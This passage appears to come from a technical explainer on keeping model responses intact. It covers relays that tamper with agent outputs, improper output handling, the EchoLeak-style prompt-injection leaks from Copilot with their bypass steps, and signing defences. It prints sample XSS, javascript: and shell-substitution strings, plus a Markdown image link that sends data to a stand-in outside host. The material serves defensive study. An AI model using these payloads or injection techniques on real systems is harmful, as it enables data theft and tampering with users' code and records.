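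Users might not notice an injection from the quality of the work. Fu and colleagues ran Claude Code with four different models and compared how often it completed the task with and without an injection. The success rate fell by 0.91 percentage points with two DeepSeek models and by about 7.3 points with Kimi-2.7 Code and Qwen3.6-Plus. Sessions grew by 0.3 to 2.1 turns on average. These results are for the crudest version of the attack, which discards one of the model's real responses.

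### Allowlists and review by a second model

Fu and colleagues also tested two defences that a developer can add without the provider's help. The first is an allowlist, which blocks any command involving an internet domain or software package that is not on the list. In the second, another model receives a summary of the task, the recent actions and the proposed action, and decides whether to allow the proposed action. The ranges below cover the four versions of the attack, each with 1,200 injections against Claude Code.

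| Defence | Injections stopped | Harmless actions, as a share of everything blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Allowlist | 31–44% | 30–44% |
| Review by DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 40–64% | 21–26% |
| Review by DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 39–62% | 9–14% |
| Review by Kimi-2.7 Code | 40–50% | 41–53% |
| Review by Qwen3.6-Plus | 51–64% | 15–20% |

The last column gives the percentage of blocked actions that were harmless. Against the crudest attack, the allowlist blocked 419 malicious actions and 231 harmless ones, so 35.5% of the 650 blocked actions were mistakes. Most harmless actions may still have gone through, but a developer who had to examine each blocked action would find about one false alarm in three. Kimi-2.7 Code did worse, stopping 582 harmless actions and 513 malicious ones against the third version.

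An allowlist fails when the harm does not involve a domain or a package. A tool call that writes a bug into one of the project's own files downloads nothing, and a quarter of the 400 injections were designed to add bugs. Liu and colleagues got a much better result from a similar defence, probably because all their attack samples were downloads or package installations, which their allowlist checks. It stopped all 1,000 samples and wrongly blocked only 1% of harmless commands. It stopped no attacks when they assumed that the attacker knew about the list and used a permitted domain or a file already on the machine.

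Liu and colleagues also tried flagging tool calls with unusual features, such as risky command patterns. This caught 89% of plain injections but only about half of those that swapped a package name or waited for a condition. It also raised false alarms on 6.7% of harmless calls.

Model review covers more kinds of harm than an allowlist, but in Fu's tests, calls that edited an existing file never triggered it. Of the 400 injections, 49 were such edits, so even a perfect reviewer would have stopped at most 88%. The reviewers also had to judge whether an action looked harmful without information about who wrote it, and a well-disguised action can look like ordinary work.

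Fu and colleagues' review results depend on connecting the reviewers directly to the model providers, which many relay users could not do. Some of the agents' built-in settings already included automatic review, but those settings blocked nothing because the review requests went through the same relay as everything else. A relay in that position can show the reviewer a harmless action in place of the malicious one, or change the verdict from "block" to "allow" on its way back. Someone who uses a relay because they cannot reach a provider directly would need a reviewer on their own machine, which Fu and colleagues did not test.

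### A patch that passes its tests

The attacks that Luo and colleagues studied are harder to notice, because the agent does what the user asked and the result works. In one case the user asked Claude Code to fix a small fault in Django, a framework for building websites. The model wrote a correct fix that kept an existing safety step, which neutralises any code hidden in text from visitors. The relay changed one line so that the website would treat that text as safe. This reopened a known type of security hole, but the reported fault was gone, all the unit tests passed, and the agent said it had verified the fix. The same happened with all five models the researchers tried.

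Luo and colleagues call this "False-Green Verification", after the green tick that marks a passed test. The public tests check whether the software works, but few check whether an attacker could abuse it. The altered line appears among the changes, so a reviewer who knows Django well could catch it. But it looks like a deliberate edit, and the comments around it are unchanged.

To measure how often this works, they took 18 Django problems from SWE-bench and found 12 in which they could reliably place such a change. With five models, that made 60 cases. A security test that the agent never saw failed in 69.0% of the altered cases, compared with 10.5% when nobody interfered. The public tests passed in 51.7% of the altered cases. The paper gives both 58.1% and 61.0% as the normal pass rate. (The altered figures fit 40 and 30 out of 58, the number of altered Django patches in a later experiment,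 better than they fit 60.)

The result is serious but weaker than the headline 69.0% suggests, because that figure includes altered cases that also failed the public tests and would have drawn attention. Between 20.7% (69.0 + 51.7 − 100) and 51.7% of all altered cases passed the public tests but failed the security test.

The evidence from APPS, a set of programming exercises, is clearer. Luo and colleagues used 100 exercises with each of the five models. With the relay interfering, 62.4% of the solutions passed the public tests, compared with 65.4% without it. Of the solutions that passed despite the interference, 99.7% contained the planted weakness. The weakness was present in 72.6% of all the exercises.

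The attack also works on agents that do not write code. On the Agent Security Bench, which tests agents in ten professional roles, the relay redirected the agent in an average of 89.1% of tasks across five models, ranging from 61.9% for Claude Opus 4.6 to 99.4% for MiniMax-M2.5. AgentDojo has 949 test cases set in banking, office work, Slack messaging and travel. There the attack succeeded 72.5% of the time, and the agents still completed 50.3% of what their users asked for.

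For comparison, the researchers tried prompt injection, in which an attacker puts instructions into something the model reads. When placed directly in the prompt, these instructions worked in 42.6% of the Agent Security Bench tasks. Luo and colleagues warn against using this figure to rank the two attacks, because prompt injection has to overcome the model's training to refuse, while the relay makes its change after the model has finished. A safer model therefore gives no protection against a dishonest relay. Luo, Fu and Liu all assume an honest provider, so their results cover only what happens after the genuine response leaves it.

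Detectors that look for suspicious content did poorly because the altered code was valid and plausible. Luo and colleagues tested seven existing defences on 353 altered APPS solutions and 58 altered Django patches, allowing each defence a false-alarm rate of 5% on normal responses. The best, which looks for improbable text, caught 30% of the APPS changes and 9% of the Django ones, while five caught none.

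Statistical differences and extra token use are more promising signs. When a relay had the same model reword the text around a change, a test that compares a service's responses with the model's own flagged 54.2% of runs, at a setting that should produce only 5% false alarms. Luo and colleagues argue, however, that nobody can statistically distinguish these reworded responses from genuine ones. The rewording also takes an extra call to the model, which roughly doubles the number of tokens used on that turn. A relay can hide this in its own usage reports, but the extra call should appear on the provider's bill if the user supplied the provider key.

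## How can an output that nobody altered harm the program that reads it?

If the program that receives a response treats part of it as code, an attacker can do harm without a relay or any other position between the model and its user. The text can arrive exactly as the model produced it (r' = r), and a hash or signature will confirm this. The harm comes from a few characters that look ordinary to a person but have a function in the program. A browser reads `<` as the start of a formatting instruction, a database may read an apostrophe as the end of a piece of text, and a shell (the program that runs typed commands) reads a semicolon as the end of a command.

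A single comma in a model's output can harm the program that reads it. *Analyzing AI Application Threat Models* (Brauchler, 2024) gives the example of an application that works with comma-separated values. Suppose each row in a hospital's file holds a name, a drug and a dose, as in `Lee,aspirin,75`. If the model writes `Lee,aspirin,low dose,75`, the next program reads "low dose" as the dose and has no field for the 75.

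OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* gives the usual name for passing a model's output to other software without adequate checking or cleaning. Because prompts can influence what the model writes, OWASP compares this to giving users indirect access to that software. The problem differs from relying too heavily on a model's accuracy, since an accurate summary can still contain a harmful script.

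### A script in a web page

Suppose the hospital's website displays a model's summary of each referral letter, and one letter contains the text `<script>alert("Hello")</script>`.

1. The model copies this text into its summary.
2. The hospital's server pastes the summary into a page written in HTML, the language of web pages, and sends the page to the doctor's browser.
3. The browser reads `<script>` as the start of a program, so it does not display what follows as text.
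4. It runs the program, which opens a small box with the word "Hello".

The box is harmless, but the browser runs the script with the permissions of the hospital's page. Another script in its place could read the patient's record from the screen or send requests as the doctor. Security engineers call this cross-site scripting.

### An image link that carries data out

Data can also leak without any script. Chat models often write in Markdown, a notation for headings, links and images that the chat software converts to HTML. A Markdown image consists of a caption and an address, and the browser fetches the image from that address as soon as it displays the answer.

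Suppose a doctor asks an assistant about a patient and the answer includes `![scan](//outsider.example/dot.png?clinic=oncology)`. The browser requests dot.png from the server at outsider.example. The request includes everything after the question mark, which the server can record. The outsider then knows which clinic the patient attends, even if the image does not exist and the doctor sees only a broken picture. An ordinary link can send the same data, but only if someone clicks on it.

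*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) explains that a model receives the user's question and the documents it reads as one sequence of tokens, and cannot reliably distinguish the user's instructions from those in the documents. An instruction hidden in a document can therefore make the model write such a link. Willison's "trifecta" combines three things that together make data theft possible: access to private data, exposure to text from an attacker, and a way to communicate with the outside. The image address provides the third.

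### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot is an assistant that searches a company's emails, files and chats to answer employees' questions. In January 2025, the research team Aim Labs reported to Microsoft that an outsider could steal this data by sending one email. The team named the flaw EchoLeak, and its number in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities is CVE-2025-32711.

*Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes how the attack worked. The email sat in the inbox until the employee asked Copilot a question and Copilot retrieved the email as relevant. To make retrieval more likely, the researchers wrote one long email that repeated the same instructions under headings such as employee onboarding, HR questions and leave of absence. Microsoft had a classifier to catch hidden instructions, but this email appeared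 to address its human recipient and never mentioned AI. It asked for the most sensitive information available and told the reader not to refer to the email.

The data then had to pass two more defences. Microsoft's filter removed outside links and images from Copilot's answers, but only when the address directly followed the caption. It missed Markdown's reference form, `![scan][ref]`, which puts the address on a separate line.

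The other defence was a content security policy, a website's list of the places from which the browser may load images, scripts and other material. The attacker's server was not on the list, but many of Microsoft's own services were. One of them, part of Microsoft Teams, would fetch any address that a request included. The browser contacted Teams, which passed the request, with the stolen data in it, to the attacker. This version of the attack required no click from the victim, unlike an earlier one that used SharePoint in the same way but required the victim to accept an invitation first.

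The attack could expose anything in Copilot's context, including the chat history and any emails or files it had retrieved. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), a Spanish government record, rates its severity at 9.3 out of 10. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, so customers had nothing to install, and that the details became public on 11 June. Microsoft found no evidence that anyone had used the flaw in a real attack. The paper adds that Copilot has since begun to strip reference-style links and embedded images from outside content.

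The demonstrated harm was to confidentiality, although Ravia calls the result a complete compromise of Copilot's "data integrity". Delivery integrity held, because the browser received what Copilot sent. Computation integrity also held, because the attacker's email was part of the input Copilot had assembled. The official vulnerability record, GCVE (2025), classifies EchoLeak as a failure to neutralise special elements in output that another component uses. That classification also fits the script example.

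### The same leak before and after EchoLeak

The method was not new, although the lack of a click was. Willison (2025) noted in a blog post on the day of the disclosure that a dozen products, including Copilot itself, had already had similar leaks. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes a flaw from February 2024 in which a phishing email made Copilot search the inbox and hide what it found as invisible characters in a link, which the user then had to click.

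In June 2026, the security company Varonis disclosed another Copilot flaw, SearchLeak (CVE-2026-42824). The victim clicked a link to Microsoft's own website whose address contained instructions for Copilot. Copilot then searched the victim's data and put the results in an image address. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) lists sign-in codes, emails and meeting details among the data at risk. Copilot's software cleaned its answers, but OffSeq's *New attack turned Microsoft 365 Copilot into 1-click data theft tool* reports that the browser acted on the image tag before the cleaning finished. The image address pointed to Bing, which the content security policy allowed, and Bing's image search fetched the attacker's address.

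The closest successor to EchoLeak came from the same research team, now called Cato AI Labs. On 3 December 2026, Simonovich's *ReLeak* (2026) disclosed three more ways to steal data from Copilot with an email and no click. One again put the data in an image address and sent it to the attacker through Bing, according to Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026). According to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), the other two used a link to a saved file and a piece of code, and a documented block on outgoing traffic failed to stop the leak. Cato knows of no real attacks using these methods. Its researchers concluded that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak, as quoted in Faisal's *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (2026).

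| Copilot flaw | What the victim had to do | How the data left | Microsoft's fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Found in February 2024 | Click a link in Copilot's answer | In the link's address | July 2024 |
| EchoLeak | Ask Copilot a question | In an image address, through Teams | May 2025 |
| SearchLeak | Click a link to Microsoft's website | In an image address, through Bing | Early June 2026 |
| ReLeak | Ask Copilot a question | In an image address through Bing, in a link to a saved file, or through code | Between 17 September and 15 November 2026 |

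### What each defence guarantees

**Encoding** replaces each character that has a special function with a code that stands for the same character as plain text. In HTML, `<` becomes `&lt;`, so the browser shows a `<` but does not start a tag. If the software uses the right encoding for the place where the text will appear, the program there treats the whole response as text, whatever the model wrote. OWASP therefore recommends matching the encoding to the context.

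The context can differ even within one page. The text `javascript:alert(1)` does nothing in a paragraph, but as the destination of a link it runs when someone clicks. HTML encoding doesn't change it, because it contains none of HTML's special characters. HTML encoding also leaves the image link to outsider.example unchanged, so if the chat software encodes the answer before converting the Markdown, the browser still fetches the image. Software can avoid this by displaying the Markdown as plain text, but then users also lose headings, links and tables. This is a practical reason why chat products filter markup instead of neutralising all of it.

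**Parameterised queries** do a similar job for databases. Suppose a program searches for a patient by pasting a name from the model's output between two apostrophes in a command. The name O'Brien breaks the command, because the database treats the apostrophe as the end of the name. An attacker could add their own command after the apostrophe. With a parameterised query, the program sends the command with a placeholder and supplies the name separately, so nothing in the name can change the command.

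This guarantee covers only the values. If the model writes the whole query, there is no fixed command to protect. In OWASP's example, a user asks a chat interface to delete every table in a database, and the model writes the query to do it. A read-only database account would block that query. A parameterised query also stores a script unchanged, so the script can still run when a web page later displays the stored text.

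**A content security policy** limits what the browser may load or run. A strict policy would have stopped both the "Hello" box, by forbidding scripts written into the page, and the direct request to outsider.example. But it does not control what a permitted server does with a request, and a rule about images does not stop a user from clicking a link.

Reddy and Gujral expect a strict policy to block leaks like EchoLeak, though they ran no experiments. They advise permitting only the company's own domains where needed, but this could still allow Teams and Bing, since Microsoft owns both. Bing was already on the list that Ravia published in 2025, and data later leaked through it in SearchLeak and in one of the ReLeak attacks. One insecure service on the list is therefore enough to defeat the policy. Reddy and Gujral also suggest fetching images through an intermediary that accepts only addresses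 with a valid signature, which would prevent an attacker from supplying a new address.

**Removing links or markup** guarantees that the answer no longer contains whatever the filter recognised, provided that the filter finishes before the browser processes the answer. EchoLeak used links that the filter didn't recognise, and SearchLeak took effect before the filter had finished. Removal can even create the markup it is meant to remove. A filter that deletes `<script>` once from `<scr<script>ipt>` leaves `<script>` behind. It is safer to permit a few kinds of markup and reject everything else. *Trust No AI* reports that Amazon responded more simply to a similar leak in its assistant Amazon Q for Business, by no longer rendering links.

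### One string in a browser and a shell

In HTML, the tags in the string `<b>$(date)</b>` make the text between them bold. In a typical Unix shell, `$(date)` runs the harmless program `date` and inserts the current date and time. A script tag could replace the bold tags, and a command that deletes files could replace `date`.

HTML encoding turns the string into `&lt;b&gt;$(date)&lt;/b&gt;`, so a browser shows the original characters instead of bold text. But if a program puts the encoded text between double quotation marks in a shell command meant only to print it, such as `echo "&lt;b&gt;$(date)&lt;/b&gt;"`, the shell still runs `date`, because HTML encoding does not change the dollar sign or the parentheses. Without the quotation marks, the shell also treats every `&` and `;` as the end of a command. The encoding added four of each, so the shell splits the line into eight commands.

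For a shell, the program should put the original string between single quotation marks, which turn off the special meaning of everything between them. The shell then passes on `<b>$(date)</b>` without running `date`. The program must handle any apostrophe in the text separately, or the quotation ends early. Single quotation marks don't turn off markup in a web page, so the browser displays them and makes the text between them bold.

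| Form of the string | In a web page | In a shell command |
|---|---|---|
| Original | Browser makes `$(date)` bold | Shell runs date, if the string is between double quotation marks |
| Encoded for HTML | Browser shows the original characters | Shell still runs date |
| Quoted for the shell | Browser still makes `$(date)` bold | Shell passes on the original characters |

Sometimes a string passes through both a shell and a browser, for example when a shell command writes a web page. The program should then encode the string for HTML first and add the shell's quotation marks last, because the shell removes its quotation marks and leaves the HTML encoding for the browser. Starting the second program directly, with the text as a separate argument, is usually safer than using the shell. The text then never becomes part of a command, as with a parameterised query.

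### Encoding and stripping compared

Encoding keeps every character. If e is the encoding and d is the browser's decoding, then d(e(r)) = r for every response r, and the doctor reads exactly what the model wrote. The encoded text has a different hash from r, so software that compares hashes should compare them before it encodes the response.

Stripping deletes characters, and the doctor cannot recover them from what is left. Suppose the model writes "Platelets <20, haemoglobin >120", and a crude filter deletes everything from each `<` to the next `>` as if it were a tag. The doctor reads "Platelets 120", so a dangerously low platelet count now looks only mildly low. The altered text is complete and plausible, so the doctor has no reason to suspect anything is missing. HTML encoding would have preserved both values.

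A better filter would leave this sentence alone, because the name of an HTML tag cannot begin with a digit. But even a filter that makes no mistakes may remove a link to the study that supports the model's advice. Stripping is a form of redaction, so the software should announce it, for instance with a visible marker such as "link removed" at the gap. (Filters for names and passwords delete content too, but they have to recognise meaning as well as markup.)

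Encoding has the opposite weakness, because it keeps everything in the answer, including private data. If the software displays the address at outsider.example as plain text, the browser will not fetch it, but the doctor can still copy it into the address bar and send the data.

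## How can a recipient prove that a response arrived unaltered?

The provider can sign each response, and the hospital's software can check the signature against the response that arrived. A relay that changes 5 mg to 50 mg cannot produce a valid signature for the changed response, so the check fails and the software refuses the order.

Signing is fast. *VeriRouter* (Yao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) reports an average of 3.84 milliseconds for a signed certificate that ties a response to the request the provider received. The practical difficulty is that honest relays also change messages.

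### Honest changes and canonical form

Most model services exchange data as JSON, a text format made up of named fields. A model's drug order might leave the provider as `{"drug":"aspirin","mg":5}`. A relay that reads this and writes it out again may send `{"mg": 5, "drug": "aspirin"}`. Any program would read both as the same drug order, but the characters differ, so the hashes differ and a signature over the original no longer matches. Relays may also reassemble streamed responses or translate between providers' formats. Luo and colleagues found that a signature over the raw message rejected legitimate responses when a relay reordered even one field. A hospital whose software kept rejecting good responses would probably switch the check off.

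The remedy is a canonical form, one agreed way of writing equivalent data. The provider converts the response to this form before signing it, and the recipient does the same before checking the signature. If the rule is to sort the fields by name and remove optional spaces, both versions of the aspirin order become `{"drug":"aspirin","mg":5}`. *AEX* (Guan, 2026) proposes an extension to existing model services that uses a published standard for canonical JSON. The standard also treats 5 and 5.0 as the same number.

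A canonical form must not merge messages that some program would treat differently. Suppose a relay sends `{"mg":5,"mg":50}`. JSON programs differ on whether they keep the first or last value of a repeated field. If the checking software reads 5 and the pharmacy's software reads 50, the signature check passes and the patient gets the wrong dose. Guan's scheme avoids this by accepting only data with unique field names.

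### sign-c: signing what the agent will execute

Luo and colleagues' scheme, sign-c, signs only the parts of a response that determine what the agent does. It adds a gateway beside the model and a small program called a shim beside the agent, and neither the model nor the agent has to change.

1. The gateway extracts the tool calls, in order, with each call's identifier, tool name and arguments. It also takes the finish reason, a field that states why the model stopped.
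2. It puts them into a canonical form, κ(c), where c stands for the extracted fields.
3. It signs b = (s, t, H(κ(q)), H(κ(c))), where s is the session, t is the turn in the conversation, q is the request and H is the hash.
4. The shim works out the same four values from the request it sent and the response it received, and checks them against the signature.
5. If a value differs, or the signature is missing or invalid, the shim discards the response before the agent can act.

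If a relay changes a dose from 5 mg to 50 mg, the hash H(κ(c)) changes and the shim rejects the order. Reordering the fields doesn't change the canonical form κ(c), so the agent proceeds.

In the researchers' tests, sign-c rejected every tampered response, including the 353 altered APPS solutions and 58 altered Django patches that content detectors mostly missed. On AgentDojo with Claude Opus 4.6, the attack's success rate fell from 74.6% to zero. The agent completed 80.9% of its users' tasks under attack, compared with 87.2% when nobody attacked, presumably because discarding a tampered response can leave the task unfinished.

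The shim rejected none of 694 untampered responses. If those responses were independent samples, the true rate of false rejections would be below about 0.4% with 95% confidence. But the test used only one relay program, new-api, and covered only reordered fields and changed spacing. It did not cover reassembled streams or translation between providers' formats, which seem more likely to cause false rejections.

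The median delay was 2.97 ms per call, or 0.0167% of the 17,796 ms that the model took to respond. The percentage is small partly because these responses were slow. The same delay would be about 0.3% of a one-second response, which is still negligible.

Luo and colleagues also varied how much of each message the signature covered, using 439 pairs of original and altered responses. The signature check caught no attacks when the signature left out the fields the agent executes. If the signature included the surrounding prose, the check rejected every response whose text the relay had reformatted.

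### What a relay can still do with unsigned prose

Sign-c protects the hospital's drug order but not its diagnosis. A relay can change "signs of malignancy" to "no signs of malignancy", and the signature still passes because the tool calls are the same. When a response contains no tool calls, sign-c signs little more than the finish reason, so the relay can replace the whole answer.

False text can also lead to wrong actions. A doctor may read an altered recommendation and enter the order by hand, and a programmer may copy altered code out of a chat. Some agents run code taken directly from the text of a response, and Luo and colleagues acknowledge that sign-c would need a broader canonical form to protect those agents.

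The relay may also be able to attack less directly. A model keeps no memory between turns, so the agent usually resends the earlier conversation with each request. If the relay alters the prose in one turn, the agent can send the altered text back in the next, and the model will treat it as its own earlier output. Any resulting tool call will come from the genuine model, and the gateway will sign it.

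An optional layer of sign-c encrypts the body of each message between the shim and the gateway, so that only routing information, such as the model's name, stays readable. This kind of encryption also reveals changes, so it should close most of these gaps, although Luo and colleagues list unauthenticated prose among the scheme's limitations. The drawback is that the relay can no longer filter, translate or reformat the content.

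Guan's AEX takes a different approach and signs the whole response in canonical form. A trusted intermediary that needs to change the response attaches a signed receipt, which links the hash of the version it received to the hash of the version it passed on. The hospital can then see that a named party changed the text, but the receipt doesn't show that the change was sensible. (Some signatures can survive permitted deletions without such receipts.)

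### Changes to the request

A valid signature on a response does not show that the provider received the question the hospital asked, so in sign-c the shim also signs its requests, and the gateway checks them the same way. Signing requests doesn't suit relays that add their own instructions to a request as part of the service, or that choose the model for the user.

Yao and colleagues apply zero-knowledge proofs to those relays, which let one party show that a statement is true without revealing the data behind it. The relay commits in advance to a private collection of permitted additions and a private index for choosing models, and an independent auditor reviews both. For each request, the relay proves that it kept the user's messages, added only permitted material and chose an eligible model. The scheme delayed responses by an average of 4.08 seconds (14%) when the relay chose a new model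 on every turn, and by 0.11 seconds when it kept one model for the whole conversation. It still needs the provider's signature to protect the response.

### Missing signatures

A relay that cannot forge a signature can still delete the genuine one. Suppose the hospital's software accepts unsigned responses because some of its providers do not sign theirs. The relay can then remove the signature, raise the dose and deliver what looks like an ordinary response from one of those providers. Security engineers call this a downgrade attack.

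AEX lets the client mark a signature as required, and a service that cannot supply one should then return an error. But the relay also handles the request and can remove the mark, so the client has to enforce the rule itself. In sign-c, the shim stores in advance which routes must carry signatures and which public key belongs to each. On those routes, it treats a missing signature as a failure. The relay can still block the response, but the user will notice.

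The shim must get the keys and rules through a channel that the relay does not control. Otherwise the relay could supply its own public key and sign the altered responses. If the shim can reach the provider directly, it can download the key from the provider's website over TLS. If all traffic must pass through the relay, the keys can be built into the shim, much as browsers come with a list of websites they must contact over an encrypted connection. Built-in keys fail to protect the user if the shim was downloaded from the relay's operator.

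### Replayed responses

An old signature remains valid for the response it came with. Suppose an agent asks for a patient's dose every morning in the same words. On Monday the model answers "5 mg", and on Tuesday, after looking up a new blood test, it answers "stop the drug". A relay can replace Tuesday's answer with Monday's, along with Monday's genuine signature. Signing a hash of the request along with the response does not prevent this, because the two requests are identical.

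The signature therefore has to cover something that never repeats. In sign-c, this is the combination of session and turn. In AEX and VeriRouter, the client puts a fresh value in each request and rejects a response whose signature covers any other value. Guan leaves the fresh value optional in AEX for compatibility but strongly encourages it.

Large providers have accepted replayed data. Their models' hidden reasoning reaches the user as an encrypted block, which the user's software sends back on the next turn. In *Let's talk about encrypted reasoning* (May 2026), Green asked whether someone could replay a block out of order, or in a different session or account. Snyk's *Stealing Reasoning Traces from Proprietary LLM APIs* (2026) reported that Anthropic, OpenAI and Google did not tie their blocks to the conversations they came from, and that its researchers had used this to extract hidden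 reasoning as readable text. The attack breached confidentiality, but the underlying mistake was to authenticate a block without authenticating its place in a conversation.

### Truncated responses

Many services stream a response in small chunks as the model writes it. A relay can cut the stream short, so that "Continue aspirin unless the platelet count falls" becomes "Continue aspirin". Signing each chunk separately would not reveal the cut, because every chunk that arrives is genuine.

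AEX links the chunks with a chain of hashes. In simplified form, the chain starts with h₀, a hash of the request, and continues with

hᵢ = H(hᵢ₋₁, i, chunkᵢ).

The provider signs the last value, hₙ, at the end of the stream. If a relay drops, reorders or edits chunk 3 of 5, then h₃, h₄ and h₅ all change and the signature check fails. If the relay cuts the stream short, the signature never arrives.

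The drawback is that the client cannot verify anything until the stream ends. AEX therefore allows signed checkpoints along the way, which let the client distinguish a stream that was cut off after a verified beginning from one with no verified part. A verified beginning can still mislead when the rest is missing, as "Continue aspirin" does.

Timing matters more for an agent, because it may run a tool call before the rest of the response arrives. If the model first cancels an old drug order and then places a new one, a response cut off between the two calls can leave the patient with neither drug. The safe choice is to hold all tool calls until the client has verified the complete response, which makes the agent slower.

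### AEGIS: a relay whose operator cannot read the traffic

All of these schemes need the provider's cooperation. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* describes an alternative called AEGIS, which changes the relay rather than the provider's service. The code that handles requests and responses runs in an attested enclave. The operator still controls login, billing and the choice of provider account, which stay outside the enclave, but never sees the content.

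The client checks the enclave before it sends anything private.

1. A small program on the user's machine sends the enclave a random number.
2. The enclave returns a statement, signed by the hardware platform, that contains a hash of the code it loaded, the random number and a hash of the certificate for this TLS connection.
3. The program checks the signature, confirms that debugging is off and compares the code hash with an approved one. The random number rules out an old statement, and the certificate hash shows that the connection ends inside the enclave.
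4. Only then does it send the prompt and the user's credential for the relay. If any check fails, it sends nothing.

The enclave forwards the body of the request and the response byte for byte. If the enclave and both encrypted connections are secure, the chance that the provider receives an altered request or the client accepts an altered response is negligible, though the operator can still make a request fail. The client can detect a change to any chunk as it arrives, so an agent that acts before the response is complete is still acting on genuine data. The enclave passes on the end-of-stream marker only when the provider has finished, so the client can tell if a response was truncated.

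The permitted destinations are part of the approved code, so the operator cannot secretly send traffic through another reseller. But one of the three services the researchers connected, OpenRouter, was itself a relay, so for that route the guarantee covers only the path between the client and OpenRouter.

AEGIS added a median delay of 5.7 ms to small requests. The same relay code outside an enclave added 3.7 ms, so the protection accounted for about 2 ms. The delay grew to 183 ms for a 4 MB request, and opening each new session took another 12 ms.

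The trusted part of the relay is 851 lines long, and its length matters because someone has to read it. Attestation identifies code but doesn't show that the code is benign, so a program that multiplied every dose by ten could still have a valid attestation. A reviewer therefore has to read the source code, build it and confirm that the result has the approved hash. To test how easy the code is to review, the researchers planted ten faults in a minimal version and gave it to two coding agents. Claude Code found all ten and Codex found eight, and neither raised a false alarm on the clean version. The researchers treat this as a pilot, and a malicious author would presumably hide a fault more carefully than they did.

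AEGIS also gives the hospital no proof that it can show anyone else. Its software can confirm that the response arrived unaltered, but an auditor a year later would have to trust the hospital. The auditor could still verify a provider's signature if the hospital had kept the response and the public key.

### Physical attacks on enclaves

AEGIS assumes that the enclave hardware is sound. It excludes physical attacks and leaks through side channels, such as the timing of memory access.

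TEE.fail, an attack published in October 2025 by researchers from Georgia Tech, Purdue University and the company Synkhronix, shows how much depends on this assumption. Using equipment they built for less than $1,000, the researchers placed a device between a server's memory module and its motherboard and recorded the encrypted data passing between the processor and memory. The processors they attacked, from Intel and AMD, always encrypt the same data at the same memory address in the same way, so repeated patterns reveal information about the contents. From these patterns the researchers recovered secret keys, including keys that sign attestations.

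An attacker with such a key can run any code on an ordinary machine and sign a statement that the approved code is running in an enclave, and all the client's checks will pass. Intel and AMD consider physical attacks of this kind out of scope for their enclaves.

The TEE.fail attack requires physical access to the server, which a relay operator has if it owns the machine. The AEGIS prototype runs on Amazon's Nitro Enclaves, a different design that TEE.fail did not target. These servers are in Amazon's data centres, so a relay operator who rents them has no physical access, but the client then has to trust Amazon.

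### Tamper-evident logs

Organisations also use logs to show that a record hasn't changed since it was made. In the simplest design, each entry's hash is computed from the entry and the previous hash, as in AEX's chain of chunks. If someone edits entry 3 of 1,000, every hash from the third onwards changes, and an auditor who kept a copy of the last hash will see the difference. If no copy is stored elsewhere, an intruder could edit the entry and recalculate the rest of the chain undetected.

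Large public logs arrange the hashes in a tree. The log's software hashes each entry, then hashes the results in pairs, and repeats this until one value, the root, remains. The log's operator signs the root. An inclusion proof shows that an entry is in the log by supplying the neighbouring hash at each level of the tree, which takes only three hashes for eight entries and about 20 for a million. A consistency proof shows that a newer root covers everything under an older one, in the same order, with new entries only at the end. Anyone who has kept an old root can therefore detect a deleted or rewritten entry. The operator could still show different logs to different people, so readers or independent witnesses need to compare roots.

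AEGIS uses this kind of public log for approved versions of its relay code. An operator who wanted to give one client a special version would have to publish it in the log, where everyone could see it.

A hospital could also log every response it receives, but the log would not expose a dishonest relay, because the hospital can record only r'. If the relay changed 5 mg to 50 mg, the log contains 50 mg, and its hashes and proofs are all correct. Investigators could compare the log with the provider's records, if those still exist, and learn that the response changed between the provider and the hospital.

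The hospital needs the hash of r from the provider to detect the change when it happens. If the provider published the hash of every response in a public log, the hospital could request an inclusion proof for the response it received, and an altered response would have none. But the log could leak private data. If a model answers only "malignant" or "benign", anyone can hash both words and see which one matches. Guan warns about this kind of guessing. The provider could prevent it by mixing a secret random value into each hash and sending that value to the hospital with the response.

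### Do the large providers sign their responses?

*Beyond Training* (Ansari, 2026) reviewed the documentation of Anthropic, OpenAI, Google's Vertex AI and Amazon's Bedrock, and found that as of September 2026 none of them issued a certificate tying each output to its input and model. OpenAI checked the structure of tool calls but did not sign them.

Anthropic and Google use signatures, but for their own benefit. AWS's *Thinking encryption* explains that the signature field on Claude's reasoning lets the service confirm that Claude wrote the reasoning when the user's software sends it back. Google's *Thought signatures* describes a similar field that also accompanies tool calls. If the software leaves out a required signature on the next turn, Gemini 3 models return an error.

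Neither feature would protect the hospital from a relay, because the provider does the checking. Even if the provider noticed an altered dose when the conversation came back, the agent would already have placed the order. When Gemini makes several tool calls in parallel, only the first carries a signature. Google also documents two placeholder values that skip the check, for developers who import a conversation from another model.

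Ansari nevertheless rates the signing of tool calls as "currently deployable" because of these two features. The rating refers to the existing technology, and Ansari concedes that a version outsiders can verify would need further specification. *Sign your outputs* (2026), a blog post from March, argues that every major lab could sign its outputs with its existing infrastructure. *Feature Request*, a user's post on OpenAI's forum, asks for signed replies to stop relays from altering them. In August, Flores (2026) submitted *The AIRP Provenance Seal and Serving Register*, a draft internet standard meant to address the same gap, though anyone can submit such a draft.

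At least one smaller provider already signs every response. According to EigenLabs' *Verify Signature*, the signature covers a network number, the model's name, the prompt and the output, joined with no separators. This leaves the boundary between prompt and output ambiguous. Suppose a hospital sends the prompt "The dose in mg is " and the model answers "50". The same signature would also be valid for the prompt "The dose in mg is 5" and the answer "0". The hospital knows what it asked, but an auditor who saw only the signed record could be fooled. Signing the length of each part as well would remove the ambiguity.

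## How can a recipient check which model produced the response?

A seller can charge for one model and run another. The replacement may be a smaller model, a different company's model, or a compressed version of the same model that stores each weight in 8 or 4 bits instead of 16. These usually cost less to run. If the seller signs the response, the signature is valid because the seller did send that text. A signature from the model's developer would expose a reseller who switched models, but not a developer who switched models on its own customers.

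### An audit of 24 resold models

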